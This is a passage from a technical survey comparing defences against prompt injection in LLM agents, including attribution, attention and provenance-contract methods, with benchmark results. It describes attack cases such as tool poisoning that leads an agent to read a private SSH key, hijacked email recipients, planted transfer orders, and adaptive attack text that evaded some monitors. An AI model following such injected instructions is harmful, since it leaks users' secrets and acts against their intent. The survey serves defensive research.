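| Source and sink both occur | 140 | 1 | 94 |
| Same topic as the source | 14 | 14 | 9 |
| Facts the model already knew | 6 | 1 | 3 |
| Clean runs | 40 | 0 | 0 |

NeuroTaint reliably detected exact and near-exact copies. It missed more flows when the model had rewritten the material repeatedly, because each rewrite made the text less similar to the original. The saved graph greatly helped it detect flows through memory, where Fides missed 25 of 30.

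NeuroTaint did worst on scenarios where the output merely shared a topic with the source, raising a false alarm in all 14. This is easy to overlook in the F1 score because those scenarios make up only 7% of the harmless ones. If they made up half and the error rates stayed the same, precision would fall to about 0.65. An agent that reads and writes about one subject all day could easily produce such a mix.

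Cai and colleagues call these boundary cases and emphasise how rarely NeuroTaint raised an alarm in ordinary harmless runs. That result is harder to interpret because they used a stricter similarity threshold, 0.95 instead of 0.60, for what they call "safe-control policies". If those policies covered the harmless scenarios, the detector was least sensitive in the runs where any alarm would be false. A deployed auditor could not set its threshold this way, because the harmless runs would not be identified in advance.

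### Why the comparison with Fides is uneven

Fides had an F1 below 0.667 on TaintBench. A detector that raised an alarm on every run would score 0.667, because half the runs contain flows and half are harmless. Fides's low score reflects a mismatch between the tool and the test more than the quality of its labels. Fides is designed to stop calls that untrusted text might have influenced. When a source and a sink occur in the same run, a different page could have changed the call, so a refusal can be correct under a strict policy even though TaintBench counts it as a false alarm. Fides also avoids many refusals by hiding untrusted text from the main model, but TaintBench doesn't measure this benefit because it scores only alarms.

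Fides, the baseline, raised no alarms in the 80 scenarios from four of the frameworks. A problem with how it connected to those frameworks' tools seems more likely than 40 separate misses. But excluding the four frameworks raises its F1 only to 0.58, so they don't account for most of the gap.

NeuroTaint and Fides perform almost equally on benchmarks that other researchers built. On the basic version of InjecAgent, a set of more than a thousand injection scenarios, NeuroTaint had an F1 of 0.994 and Fides 0.993. On 79 cases from ToolEmu, which tests agents with simulated tools, both scored 0.760. These benchmarks label unsafe actions rather than flows, so they cannot show which method traces flows better. The evidence for NeuroTaint's large advantage comes from a benchmark its own developers built.

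TaintBench's labels also describe what a scenario is designed to do, whether or not that happens in a particular run. With Claude Opus 4.6 as the agent, NeuroTaint's recall fell to 0.547. Cai and colleagues suggest that stronger models refuse some attacks before they reach a sink. If so, no flow occurs in those runs and the auditor is correct to report none, but the benchmark still counts a miss. The headline recall was therefore measured on an older, more compliant model, and the lower figure doesn't show that the auditor works worse on newer ones.

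False alarms matter less if another check follows. Cai and colleagues had models review the 203 runs that NeuroTaint had flagged and decide whether the call in each was unsafe. Claude Opus 4.6 dismissed all 16 false alarms but also 8 of the 187 real flows. GPT-4.1 mini also dismissed all 16 false alarms, along with 61 of the real flows.

NeuroTaint's audit takes an average of 0.25 seconds per run, and each query to the judging model uses about 457 tokens. The audit might be fast enough to use before a call, but Cai and colleagues tested it only afterwards. Used that way, it can report that a page supplied an email's recipient only after the email has been sent.

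## Measuring influence through attention and removed inputs

NeuroTaint's final test uses another model to guess what the agent would have done with different text. Software can test this directly by running the agent's model on the same input without the page and checking whether the call changes. It can also record which parts of the input the model attends to while it writes the call. Both approaches can detect influence even when no text from the page appears in the argument.

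### Removing one segment of the input

A language model gives every possible next token a probability. To find the probability of a whole argument, software feeds the argument to the model one token at a time and multiplies the probabilities of its tokens. The *leave-one-out score* compares the result with and without one segment of the input:

```
score(s, a) = log p(a | C) − log p(a | C without s)
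```

Here `a` is the argument's value, `C` is the full context and `s` is the segment, such as the text of a web page. The score is positive if the segment made the value more likely and negative if the segment made it less likely.

Take an invented example in which the model writes the stranger's address with a probability of 0.90 when the page is in its input and 0.02 when it isn't:

```
ln 0.90 − ln 0.02 = ln 45 ≈ 3.8
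```

The page made the address 45 times as likely. For the correct email, the probability of the manager's address might be 0.98 with the page and 0.97 without it, which gives a score of about 0.01.

The score measures influence as the counterfactual definition describes it, and both make it hard to separate what triggers a call from what determines its arguments. To score the recipient alone, the software can supply the call up to the start of the address and measure only the address.

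Removing the only text that contains an address almost always produces a high score, because a model can rarely produce an address that isn't in its input. Dora's website would get a high score even for the Slack invitation that the user asked for. A high score is therefore not evidence of an attack, and a defence needs something to compare it with.

### Comparing the page with the user's request

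Kim, Parmar and colleagues (2026), in *CausalArmor*, compare it with the score of the user's request. They expect the request to have the most influence on a normal call. In a successful injection, the request does little to make the malicious call more likely, while one untrusted segment does a lot. Their defence, which they published in February 2026, works as follows:

1. The agent proposes a consequential call, such as sending a message or making a payment. Other calls run without a check.
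2. A smaller model, Gemma 3 12B, computes the probability of the proposed call with the full context, without the user's request, and without each tool result in turn.
3. CausalArmor calculates the leave-one-out scores and divides each by the number of tokens in the model's output, so that longer outputs don't get larger scores just for their length.
4. It flags any tool result whose score is too high compared with the request's score.
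5. Another model rewrites the flagged results, removing instructions and keeping facts that the request needs.
6. CausalArmor replaces the agent's reasoning since the first flagged result with a placeholder, and the agent chooses its action again.

The rule in the fourth step is:

```
score(result) > score(request) − τ
```

With the default margin, τ = 0, CausalArmor flags a result only if it outweighs the request. A larger margin flags more results.

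The sixth step is there because the agent may already have accepted the planted instruction in its reasoning and could still follow it after it is removed from the page. Leaving out this step raised the average attack success rate from 0.29% to 1.75%. CausalArmor runs the agent's new action without checking it again, so its security depends heavily on the rewriting.

Kim and colleagues tested CausalArmor on AgentDojo with three wordings of the attack. The table gives the highest success rate among the three.

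| Agent's model | Tasks completed without an attack, undefended | With CausalArmor | Highest attack success rate, undefended | With CausalArmor | Running time without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 54% | 56% | 32.5% | 0.6% | 1.30 times |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 89% | 82% | 19.0% | 0.5% | 1.27 times |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 93% | 87% | 8.9% | 0.1% | 1.22 times |

PromptArmor, which rewrites every tool result, stopped about as many attacks on Gemini 3 Pro as CausalArmor, but the agent completed only 77% of the tasks and took 1.78 times as long as it did with no defence. CausalArmor preserved more of the agent's usefulness because it rewrites only the flagged results. In a harder test, the attacker could read the conversation and alter a shop's product catalogue to suit it. CausalArmor lowered the attack success rate in that test from 89% to 3.7%.

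Kim and colleagues also derive a limit on the probability that an agent makes any malicious call in `T` steps:

```
P(attack succeeds) ≤ T · m · e^−(β + γ)
```

Here `m` is the number of possible malicious actions, and `β` and `γ` are differences in log-probability. `β` is how strongly the model prefers the correct action without the flagged text, and `γ` is how much the rewritten text adds to that preference. The proof assumes that both are positive, but `γ` is positive only if the rewriting worked. The formula therefore describes what follows from successful rewriting but gives no reason to expect the rewriting to succeed.

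CausalArmor scores the agent's whole output instead of each argument. Most of the email to the manager is a summary that depends on the page, so the page could outweigh the request even without an attack. This would do little harm, because the rewriting should leave the facts about customs rules in place. But an adapter can't use the score to identify a bad recipient in an email whose body is fine.

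### Weakening the page instead of removing it

Deleting a page removes its facts along with its instructions. He, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *AttriGuard*, keep the facts and weaken the language that might direct the agent. They define the *control effect* of the tool results on a call `c`:

```
control effect(c) = log p(c | C) − log p(c | C₀)
```

`C₀` is an ideal context in which the tool results still inform the agent but can't steer it. Nobody can construct this context exactly, and many commercial models don't reveal the probabilities. AttriGuard, released in March 2026, approximates the comparison by running the agent's model a second time:

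1. The agent proposes one or more tool calls.
2. An auxiliary model rewrites the latest tool results. It turns structured data into prose and replaces direct commands with reports of what the text says. A stricter setting also weakens claims that some action is necessary.
3. The agent's model runs again with the user's request, the actual record of earlier calls, and the rewritten results.
4. A proposed call survives if the second run contains the same call. If the tool matches but the arguments differ, another model judges whether the proposed call is consistent with the request.
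5. AttriGuard executes the surviving calls. For the others, it gives the agent an empty result and a warning.

Reusing the actual record prevents harmless differences between the two runs from accumulating. The agent still works from the original text, because rewriting can damage details it needs. In a test with GPT-4.1 mini, running the agent on the rewritten results lowered the share of completed tasks from 71% to 62%.

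He et al. compared AttriGuard with other defences on AgentDojo, using four fixed attacks. Only AttriGuard and CaMeL stopped all four completely. When there was no attack, AttriGuard completed 67% of tasks with Gemini 2.5 Flash, compared with 38% for CaMeL and 58% for an undefended agent. With Llama 3.3 70B, the figures were 54%, 37% and 60% respectively. A check that only blocks calls shouldn't raise the completion rate, so the gain over the undefended agent on Gemini may come from chance or from an instruction that AttriGuard adds to the prompt.

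The setting in the second step strongly affects how many attacks succeed. When AttriGuard only turned structured data into prose, 12% of attacks of one type succeeded against GPT-4.1 mini. Replacing the commands as well reduced this to zero.

Fixed attacks are a weak test, so He and colleagues also used a program that used knowledge of how each defence worked to refine its attack text over 200 attempts. On 61 cases with Gemini, the program succeeded in 6.6% of cases against AttriGuard, 30% against PromptArmor and 82% against MELON. MELON, which removes the user's request and looks for calls the agent would make anyway, had stopped every fixed attack on the same cases. Neither CausalArmor nor the other systems discussed below went through this test.

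Every attack that beat AttriGuard aimed to make the agent visit a particular website. The program succeeded by mentioning that the site had more detailed information, which made visiting it look like a sensible part of the task. Because the text contained no command to weaken, AttriGuard let the call through.

### Reading the model's attention

Attention weights can be used to measure influence with little extra computation, because the model computes them anyway. When a model processes a token, it gives each earlier token a weight that determines how much information it takes from that token. It does this many times in parallel in every layer. The RTBAS screener used these weights to decide what the next message depends on.

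*MINDGUARD* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) uses attention weights to defend against *tool poisoning*, an attack that puts instructions in a tool's description. For example, a harmless-looking tool's description might include an instruction to read the user's private SSH key before creating a directory. The agent then misuses a legitimate file-reading tool, and the poisoned tool never has to run. CaMeL can miss this attack because its main model reads tool descriptions as trusted text.

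MindGuard builds a weighted graph for each tool call, connecting the user's request, each tool description and each earlier tool result to the name of the called tool and the argument values. Treating the tool name and argument values as separate targets prevents the strong attention produced by copying a value from hiding the much weaker attention produced by choosing a tool.

The software first combines the layers, giving the middle ones the most weight. Then it removes *attention sinks*, tokens that attract a lot of attention from everywhere regardless of their meaning. The weight of the edge from source `s` to target `t` is the sum of the squares of the remaining attention weights:

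```
w(s, t) = Σ A(i, j)²,  for every token i in t and every token j in s
```

Squaring the attention weights keeps many tiny ones from adding up to a large total. For example, a single weight of 0.5 would contribute 0.25, while fifty weights of 0.01 would contribute only 0.005 in total.

MindGuard then calculates a ratio for every tool that the agent did not call:

```
ratio(s, t) = w(s, t) / (w(request, t) + w(called tool, t))
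```

If the ratio exceeds a threshold for either target, MindGuard blocks the call and names that tool as the source. Earlier tool results appear in the graph, but this rule does not test them. The rule would therefore catch the stranger's address if it came from a poisoned tool description, but not if it came from a web page.

The tests used five open models, two of them both with and without reasoning. The hijacked calls came from MCPTox, a set of poisoning attacks based on real tool servers. *Average precision* measures how well a score separates hijacked calls from normal ones across all thresholds, and 100% means perfect separation. MindGuard's average precision was 94% to 99% when the normal calls came from a separate dataset with no poisoned descriptions, and 82% to 98% when they came from cases where the model had ignored a poisoned description. Among the attacks it detected, MindGuard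 identified the right tool at least 95% of the time.

With a threshold of 0.9, MindGuard caught 91% of the hijacked calls that Qwen3-8B made without reasoning. It wrongly flagged 0.9% of the normal calls made with a poisoned description present and none of the calls from the clean dataset. The analysis took less than a second and used no extra model calls.

### Whether attention shows causation

Attention shows where a model takes information from, but later layers may not use that information, and even a small amount of information may change a close decision. Wang and colleagues acknowledge that attention is not strictly causal and cite earlier research in which a single attention head could be manipulated without changing the output. They reply that their score combines all heads and layers, which would be much harder for an attacker to manipulate, and that the attention weights of commercial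 models are private. They also argue that a planted instruction can't change a call unless the model attends to it.

The argument is plausible, but the paper offers little evidence for it. It gives two examples of subtle attacks that worked on Qwen3-8B with reasoning, with ratios of 0.51 and 0.38. A threshold of 0.9 would miss both attacks. Lowering it to 0.3 would catch them, but at 0.3 MindGuard wrongly flagged 30% of normal calls with a poisoned description present and 8% of those without one. The paper also proves that any call passing the check meets its definition of security, but this definition measures influence by the attention weights themselves, so the proof can't show that the weights reflect causes.

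### Labels for every token inside the model

An open-source project called *Isotope* also uses attention, but tracks sources through every layer of the model. Each token in the input starts with a label that assigns 100% of its content to one source, such as the user or a particular document. Each layer then mixes the labels in proportion to the information it moves between tokens:

```
U′(t) = (1 − α) · U(t) + α · Σⱼ W(t, j) · U(j)
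```

`U(t)` lists each source's share of position `t` before the layer, and `U′(t)` lists the shares after it. `W(t, j)` is an adjusted attention weight, and `α` is the share of the new content that came from attention. As an invented example, suppose `α` is 0.2, a position is labelled entirely as the user's, and half of its attention weight is on a web page. After this layer, the page's share of that position is 0.2 × 0.5 = 0.1.

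When the model writes a token, the token inherits the shares computed at the position that produced it. The label therefore survives the step at which ordinary taint tracking loses it. The final score ignores the system prompt, which accounts for most of every label, and compares untrusted content with the user's:

```
untrusted share / (untrusted share + user's share)
```

Isotope scores each argument of a call separately. On the tasks its developers used to choose thresholds, recipients the user supplied scored at most 0.19, and recipients an attacker supplied scored at least 0.71. The bodies of legitimate emails scored 0.55 to 0.60, and Isotope does not restrict them. It can also flag the decision to make a call, even if the user mentioned the recipient. One of its tests involves a colleague whom the user explicitly said not to email.

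The evidence for Isotope is very limited. Its developers wrote all 26 test tasks themselves, tested only one small model with 1.5 billion parameters, and included the tasks they used for tuning in the results. None of the 16 attacks succeeded, compared with seven against the undefended model, and nine of the ten harmless tasks worked. The scores depend on how the calculation treats attention. A standard method that sets `α` to 0.5 and averages all heads equally gave the attacks an influence score close to zero. Isotope describes its score as an upper bound on influence, but it measures how much content moves, and a small amount could still change the result.

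### Inferring a dependency graph

A language model can also work out the dependencies from the record of the agent's run. *AGENTARMOR* (Wang, Liu et al., 2025) treats that record like a program and analyses it before each tool call. A model reads the earlier prompts, tool results and the agent's reasoning, and identifies which of them led to the choice of tool (a *control dependency*) and which supplied each argument (a *data dependency*).

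AgentArmor combines these into a graph and adds effects missing from the record, such as the local folder created when a tool copies a code repository. It then gives every node an integrity level and a confidentiality level. A node that depends on several sources gets the join of their levels. AgentArmor's *type checker* blocks the run if untrusted data flows into a node that requires trusted data, or if secret data flows into a less protected node.

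For the email to the manager, a correct graph would connect the recipient to the user's request and the body to the page. The two arguments could therefore have different labels, even though the agent's model read everything at once. Control dependencies cover calls with no arguments to trace. *AgentTracer* (Yao, Wu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a planted instruction that makes an agent add the attacker's SSH key to a code repository and later clear its own memory. The memory-clearing call has no arguments, so data dependencies can't connect it to the page.

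On AgentDojo, AgentArmor reduced the attack success rate from 41% to 3%, while the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell only from 73% to 72%. CaMeL stopped every attack in the same comparison but completed 48% of the tasks. AgentArmor relies on an inference that can be wrong, as Wang, Liu and colleagues acknowledge. Overlooking a page has worse consequences than in RTBAS, which removes any page that its screener overlooks, whereas AgentArmor's agent has already read the page and the resulting call passes as trusted. Like NeuroTaint's judge, the analysing model reads the page, so an attacker could try to mislead it.

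### When two sources support the same value

Leave-one-out scores can miss an input's influence when another input is enough to produce the same argument. In another invented example, two pages contain the same instruction, and the stranger's address has a probability of 0.90 with both pages, 0.88 with either one and 0.02 with neither. Removing one page gives a score of about 0.02, and removing both gives 3.8.

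CausalArmor's comparison with the request helps a little. If the request does nothing to make the stranger's address more likely, even a score of 0.02 outweighs it. But with scores this small, a slight change in the request's score could reverse the outcome. Kim and colleagues recognise that an attacker might spread influence over several tool results, though they argue that an attack usually needs one decisive instruction. They suggest testing groups of results in future work. Ten results can form 1,023 groups, so a system could test only some of them.

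AttriGuard avoids the problem by weakening all the tool results at once, although its test can't show which page was responsible.

If the user and the page both give the manager's address, the model should make the same call in AttriGuard's second run. Attention is harder to interpret in this case because the model might copy the address from the page even though the user's request alone would have been enough.

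### When the argument has to come from the page

Dora's website strongly influences the address in her invitation. If CausalArmor flags the website, CausalArmor's rewriting should keep the address, because the request needs it. AttriGuard should keep it too, so both would correctly allow the call. But if an attacker replaced the address on the website without adding any instruction, the false address would probably pass too, because these defences mainly detect text that directs the agent.

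Delegation is harder still, as in the AgentDojo tasks that tell the agent to do what a file says. Kim and colleagues show a run in which the file was a landlord's notice of a rent increase, with a planted order to transfer money. CausalArmor removed the order, and the agent then looked up the rent payment in order to change the amount. AgentArmor has a setting that permits or forbids following instructions in a file. Permitting it lets more attacks through, while forbidding it blocks more legitimate tasks.

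In their AgentDojo tests, He et al. excluded cases where the user had given untrusted text full control over the action the attacker wanted. They point out that attribution can't verify whether such text is authentic.

Removal tests can also mislead investigators after an attack, because removing a legitimate step can prevent the harmful call and make that step look like a possible source. Yao and colleagues therefore compare each call with what the user authorised before tracing the attack backwards. AgentTracer found the exact point where the planted text entered in 94% of 600 successful attacks, which the researchers had hidden among the records of 9,000 harmless calls.

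### Models that keep their internals private

The methods differ in what they need and how much work they add. Many developers use commercial models that return text without attention weights or the probabilities these scores need.

| System | What it needs from the agent's model | Extra model calls |
|---|---|---|
| CausalArmor | Nothing internal if another model computes the scores | One batch of *n* + 2 inputs for *n* tool results; after a flag, a rewrite of each flagged result and a new action |
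| AttriGuard | Only the model's output | A second run for every step with a tool call, rewriting of new results and sometimes a judge |
| MindGuard | Attention weights | None |
| Isotope | Attention weights and other internal values | None |
| AgentArmor | A record of the run, including any visible reasoning | Dependency analysis for each new action |

AttriGuard's extra calls raised the average time per task from 11 to 32 seconds with Gemini 2.5 Flash, and from 14 to 41 seconds with Llama 3.3 70B. MindGuard and Isotope add much less overhead, but only the company that runs the model, or someone using an open model, can install them. Isotope also requires software that calculates the full table of attention weights, a step that faster methods skip.

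CausalArmor works with closed models by having Gemma calculate scores for calls that Gemini or Claude wrote. The scores measure how the page affects Gemma, which may differ from how it affects the model that wrote the call. If a page fooled Claude but not Gemma, removing it might hardly change Gemma's probabilities. In tests on Gemini 3 Pro, stand-in models with more than 12 billion parameters detected nearly all attacks, while smaller ones missed more. An attacker who knows which open model calculates the scores can also test attacks on a copy of it, so Kim and colleagues recommend keeping the choice secret or changing it regularly.

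## Argument roles and per-argument contracts

Suppose one of these methods has shown that the web page influenced the body of the email and that the recipient came from the user. To decide whether to send the email, the adapter also needs a description of what each argument does, which can't be inferred from the origin of its value.

PACT (Provenance-Aware Capability Contracts), a monitor that Fan and colleagues released in May 2026, adds the missing information by assigning a *role* to every argument of every tool. Each role has its own rule about which sources may supply the argument's value.

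### Six roles

| Role | Typical arguments | Lowest trust that PACT accepts by default |
|---|---|---|
| Target | Recipient, web address, file path, attendee, account | User |
| Command | Shell command, query that changes data | Trusted or user, depending on the tool |
| Credential | Password, token, API key | Trusted |
| Content | Email body, summary, report, quoted text | External |
| Selector | Object ID, filter, search handle | Depends on the tool |
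| Control | Mode, overwrite, dry run | A cautious default |

The last column uses an ordered scale:

```
TRUSTED > USER > TOOL_OUTPUT > EXTERNAL
```

Trusted values are constants that the developer's own software supplies, and user values come from the request. Tool output means structured results from internal tools, while external values come from web pages, emails, retrieved files and outside services. Because the user ranks below the developer, a password that the user types into the request is not trusted enough by default to fill a credential argument.

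### Why one decision per call is not enough

Fan and colleagues prove that some monitors need a distinction of this kind. Their argument compares two calls to the same tool:

```
legitimate call:   recipient ← user    body ← page
hijacked call:     recipient ← page    body ← page
```

A monitor that makes one decision for the whole call, based on whether any argument falls below a trust threshold, treats both calls the same because both contain an argument from the page. It blocks the summary the user asked for if the threshold excludes the page, and lets the summary go to the attacker if the threshold admits it. A contract that requires user trust for the recipient but accepts external text in the body allows the legitimate call and blocks the hijacked one.

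The proof is correct, but it covers only monitors, such as RTBAS and the released version of Fides, that reduce a call to its least trusted argument. It does not cover a monitor that compares the recipient with the user's request.

All-or-nothing decisions also lower task completion with a much newer model. In *Intent Contracts*, Wang, Zhu and colleagues (2026) used GPT-6.1 Terra to plan an agent's work and looked at runs in which it added work nobody had requested. With a reviewer that could only accept or refuse whole commands, the agent completed the user's task in 16 of 30 runs. With their own design, in which a small trusted model writes each call and can leave out the extra work, it completed the task in 27.

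### The contract and the check

A PACT contract has a precision level, an entry for each argument, and a specification of how far to trust the tool's output. An entry contains the argument's name and role, its minimum trust, a set of forbidden origins, a set of obligations such as a required confirmation, and a list of procedures that may grant exceptions. A simple contract for `send_email` might look like this:

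```
send_email, level L2

argument    role      minimum trust   forbidden origins   obligations
recipient   target    USER            web_fetch           none
subject     content   EXTERNAL        none                none
body        content   EXTERNAL        none                none
```

Each value has a tag with its origins `O`, its trust level `τ` and its unmet obligations `B`. When the agent combines two values, PACT merges their tags:

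```
merge = ( O₁ ∪ O₂,  min(τ₁, τ₂),  B₁ ∪ B₂ )
```

If the body joins a greeting from the user to facts from the page, its origins are the user and `web_fetch`, and its trust is external. Before the call runs, PACT checks every value `v` against the entry for its argument:

```
τ(v) ≥ minimum trust
O(v) ∩ forbidden origins = ∅
B(v) ∪ required obligations ⊆ obligations already met
```

A single failure blocks the call, unless an exception applies.

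The first two conditions are both needed because a value can gain trust as it passes through other tools. If an internal tool reads a web page and returns a summary, PACT may label the summary as tool output, which ranks above external text. The summary's set of origins still contains `web_fetch`, however many tools the text has passed through. When Fan and colleagues stopped tracking origins across steps in a controlled test, the share of attacks that PACT blocked fell from 100% to 80%.

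Developers can describe a tool at four levels of precision:

- **L0** treats the call as a single unit and requires every argument to be trusted, so even an address that the user typed fails.
- **L1** applies one threshold to all the arguments.
- **L2** applies the rule for each argument's role.
- **L3** does the same but also accepts certificates, which grant limited exceptions.

In a test with correct labels, PACT blocked every attack at all four levels. The share of legitimate tasks it allowed rose from 8% at L0 to 58% at L1 and 100% at L2 and L3. A developer can therefore start with L0 for an unfamiliar tool and lose usefulness but not security. Moving to a finer level is safe only if the roles are labeled correctly, since marking a recipient as content would create a vulnerability that L0 did not have.

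### Certificates for exceptions

Dora's invitation to Slack fails at L2. Her address came from her website, and a target requires at least user trust. At L3 a trusted procedure, such as asking the user to confirm the address, can issue a certificate with four parts:

```
d = (r, s, ρ, τmax)
```

Here `r` is the failed check that the certificate excuses, `s` is the procedure that issued it, `ρ` is the set of roles it covers, and `τmax` is the highest trust it can confer. The certified value gets a new tag:

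```
origins:       O(v) ∪ {s}
trust:         min(τmax, τcert(s))
obligations:   B(v) without r
```

`τcert(s)` is the most trust that procedure `s` can give a value. Giving a value this trust is called *endorsement*, a deliberate and limited decision to treat an untrusted value as trusted for a stated use. The tag still records that Dora's address came from a website, and the agent can't use the address as a command.

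The scope is still fairly broad because `ρ` names roles, not individual arguments. If the contract for `send_email` accepts the same confirmation procedure, a certificate for Dora's invitation could also let the agent email her a confidential file. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes a system that builds on PACT and ties each exception to one destination field. An exception may allow a file path extracted from an error log to fill the path argument, but it doesn't allow that text to determine which tool is called or whether a change is marked as approved.

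*Agenra* (2026), a language for writing agents' permissions, requires the developer to specify such exceptions before the task begins. If Alice's address is unknown, the contract names the lookup tool, its exact arguments and the result field that may supply the recipient. Text from another tool can't supply the recipient, even if it looks like a directory entry. But if the developer names the wrong tool, the monitor can't detect the error.

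The AuthGraph defence records which tool supplied each argument and checks that it was the expected one, so a false value passes if an attacker has poisoned that tool's data. *Standing, Not Truth* (2026) quotes this limitation from the AuthGraph paper. The problem is hard to avoid when a user asks an agent to choose a product, because the user hasn't named one and the agent can only get it from the catalogue.

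Fan and colleagues' experiments give little evidence about certificates, because L2 already allowed every legitimate task in the test of the four levels and L3 had none left to recover.

### Where the labels come from

PACT's proofs assume correct contracts and a complete record of origins, but in practice software has to infer both. PACT drafts each contract from the names, types and descriptions of the arguments in the tool's schema. It labels an argument called `recipient` or `url` as a target, `password` as a credential, and `body` as content.

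To find the origin of a value, PACT tries these steps in order:

1. If the value exactly matches something the user wrote or a trusted constant, it gets that source's tag.
2. If it exactly matches a field in an earlier tool result, it gets that field's tag.
3. If it is a recognisable transformation of known sources, PACT merges their tags.
4. If the origin is still unclear and the argument is a sink argument, PACT assigns low trust.
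5. For any other argument, a language model guesses, and PACT uses a cautious label if the model's confidence is low.

The deployed system therefore relies heavily on matching. Because it checks the user's text first, an address that appears in both the request and the page counts as the user's. *AGENTCAP* (2026), another monitor, makes this an explicit rule and rejects a protected argument only if all its support comes from untrusted content. The merge rule is for values that both sources contributed to, so it doesn't apply to an address that either source could supply on its own.

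Matching also misses implicit flows. If the user supplies Amira's and Ben's addresses and the page's topic determines which one the model uses, PACT labels the address as the user's either way. The user may have wanted the page to determine the recipient, but this does not fit the assumption behind the proofs. Applying the merge rule strictly to everything the model had read would instead block the correct email to the manager.

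Under Santos-Grueiro's stricter view, a tool name copied exactly from a trusted list still counts as untrusted if untrusted text led the model to pick it. The system also requires separate permission for the call itself, since a page might cause an unwanted second payment in which every argument is legitimate. PACT does not address this kind of attack. In 400 coding tasks, Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorised action that got past the checks, and the agent completed 231 tasks safely.

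On 20 real tools, PACT's automatic pipeline assigned the right role 87.1% of the time and the right origin 77.4%. Ameur and colleagues also found roles hard to infer. Their method missed 25.9% of sink arguments on third-party tools.

The harm from wrong roles depends on the pattern of errors. When Fan and colleagues mislabelled half the roles at random, PACT still blocked 88% of attacks and allowed 72% of legitimate tasks. When they labelled every target as content, it blocked only 40% of attacks. When they labelled all content as targets, it still blocked every attack but allowed only 40% of legitimate tasks. Real errors probably resemble the two systematic cases more than the random one, because a rule based on names will make the same mistake wherever a misleading name recurs.

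Errors about origin can be worse, because if PACT gives a tool's output too much trust, none of its other safeguards corrects the mistake. Fan and colleagues consider this the most important remaining failure, and it mainly affected tasks that went from a web page to an email.

### How strong the evidence is

The first experiment used 17 scenarios with perfect labels, so it tested the rule without the inference. Fan and colleagues write that each scenario contains both a legitimate action and an attack, but their counts correspond to nine legitimate cases and eight attacks:

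| Monitor | Legitimate cases allowed | Attacks blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 9 of 9 | 0 of 8 |
| Fides, reimplemented | 6 of 9 | 3 of 8 |
| CaMeL, reimplemented | 3 of 9 | 8 of 8 |
| PACT at L2 | 9 of 9 | 8 of 8 |

PACT also made no mistakes on 50 further scenarios, or on 30 attacks and tasks written after the contracts were final. These results confirm that the software applies its rule correctly. They are weaker evidence that the rule is useful, because the researchers built the main scenarios around the distinction that PACT draws.

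AgentDojo is a harder test because PACT had to infer the roles and origins itself. The table shows the share of the 97 legitimate tasks that each agent completed, and how many of the 27 injection tasks succeeded with no defence.

| Model | No defence | Fides | CaMeL | PACT | Successful attacks with no defence |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-turbo | 20.6% | 19.6% | 11.3% | 18.6% | 2 |
| Qwen-plus | 60.8% | 59.8% | 29.9% | 45.4% | 3 |
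| Qwen-max | 46.4% | 50.5% | 29.9% | 38.1% | 1 |
| Qwen2.5-72B | 46.4% | 48.5% | 28.9% | 42.3% | 1 |
| GPT-4o mini | 59.8% | 55.7% | 30.9% | 46.4% | 3 |

With GPT-4o mini, PACT completed 15 more tasks than CaMeL and 13 fewer than the undefended agent. CaMeL stopped every attack on all five models. PACT did so on three, but the paper reports inconsistent results for the other two, Qwen-turbo and Qwen-plus. The results table gives PACT 100% security on both, whereas the text gives 96.3%, which means that one attack succeeded on each.

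The security results are weak evidence because the attacks rarely worked on undefended agents. A drop from three successes to zero in 27 attempts could easily be chance, and zero successes in 27 is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 12%. The models tested are also far behind those of late 2026, which would probably complete more tasks and resist more of these attacks, so the figures may not apply to them.

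The comparison with Fides is hard to trust. On all five models, at least as many attacks succeeded with Fides as with no defence, and on two models one more succeeded. In Costa and colleagues' tests, however, Fides's policy checks stopped every attack. On InjecAgent, Fan and colleagues' version of Fides blocked 68% of 1,598 harmful calls, while the NeuroTaint paper reports a nearly perfect F1 score for Fides. The reimplementation evidently differs from the original in ways that affect the results. The CaMeL figures are easier to believe, since CaMeL also completed about 30% of the tasks in the SecureClaw study, which ran CaMeL's released code.

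To test whether roles matter, Fan and colleagues also gave every argument the same threshold. On AgentDojo, requiring user trust for every argument stopped all the attacks, but only 14.4% of tasks were completed. Accepting external text for every argument raised completion to 18.6% but let two attacks through. PACT with roles also completed 18.6% of tasks and let one attack through. These results support roles only slightly, since PACT completed just four more tasks than the strict threshold and stopped one more attack than the lenient one. Roles mattered much more in the controlled scenarios, where removing them reduced utility from 100% to 40%.

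In a week-long trial with 280 calls to 15 tools, PACT blocked all 13 attacks and none of the 267 legitimate calls. Setting up the contracts took 75 minutes. PACT did worse on Agent-SafetyBench, a broad safety benchmark, where it blocked 74.7% of the unsafe cases and allowed 39.3% of the safe ones. Many of the benchmark's dangers, such as misinformation, are in the content itself, which PACT does not evaluate. The check takes less than 0.3 milliseconds in 99% of cases.

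*PACE* describes a later monitor that also records an origin for each argument. In its ablation, most of the security gain came from a separate check that compares the effects of a call with what the user requested.

### Whether CaMeL decides per call

CaMeL's interpreter checks each argument's tags, so a policy can require a trusted recipient and accept an untrusted body, as PACT does. Fan and colleagues say that both Fides and CaMeL check a tool call as a whole, which is wrong about CaMeL's design.

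*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) writes out the general form of such a policy. The context that produced the call has a label `ℓ`, each argument has a label `ℓᵢ`, and the policy sets a separate limit for each:

```
ℓ ⊑ π_f    and    ℓᵢ ⊑ πᵢ for every argument i
```

The simplified version of CaMeL that Ameur and colleagues wrote for their comparison also checked arguments one by one. The reimplementation that allowed only three of nine legitimate cases was therefore coarser than CaMeL has to be, and the separation proof does not apply to CaMeL as designed.

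PACT still differs from CaMeL in two useful ways. Its roles give developers a common vocabulary, so they can mark an argument as a target instead of programming a policy for each tool. It also lets the agent choose its next step after reading a page, while CaMeL needs a plan beforehand. Peters-Gill and colleagues traced most of CaMeL's failed tasks to planning in advance, so this difference may explain more of PACT's lead on AgentDojo than roles do.

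### Arguments with more than one role

Arguments with the same name can have different roles. A `query` is content when a search engine looks for matching pages, but a command when a database runs it and changes records. An `id` may select an object or act as a trusted handle to one. Fan and colleagues decide such cases tool by tool and choose the stricter role when in doubt, which blocks some legitimate calls.

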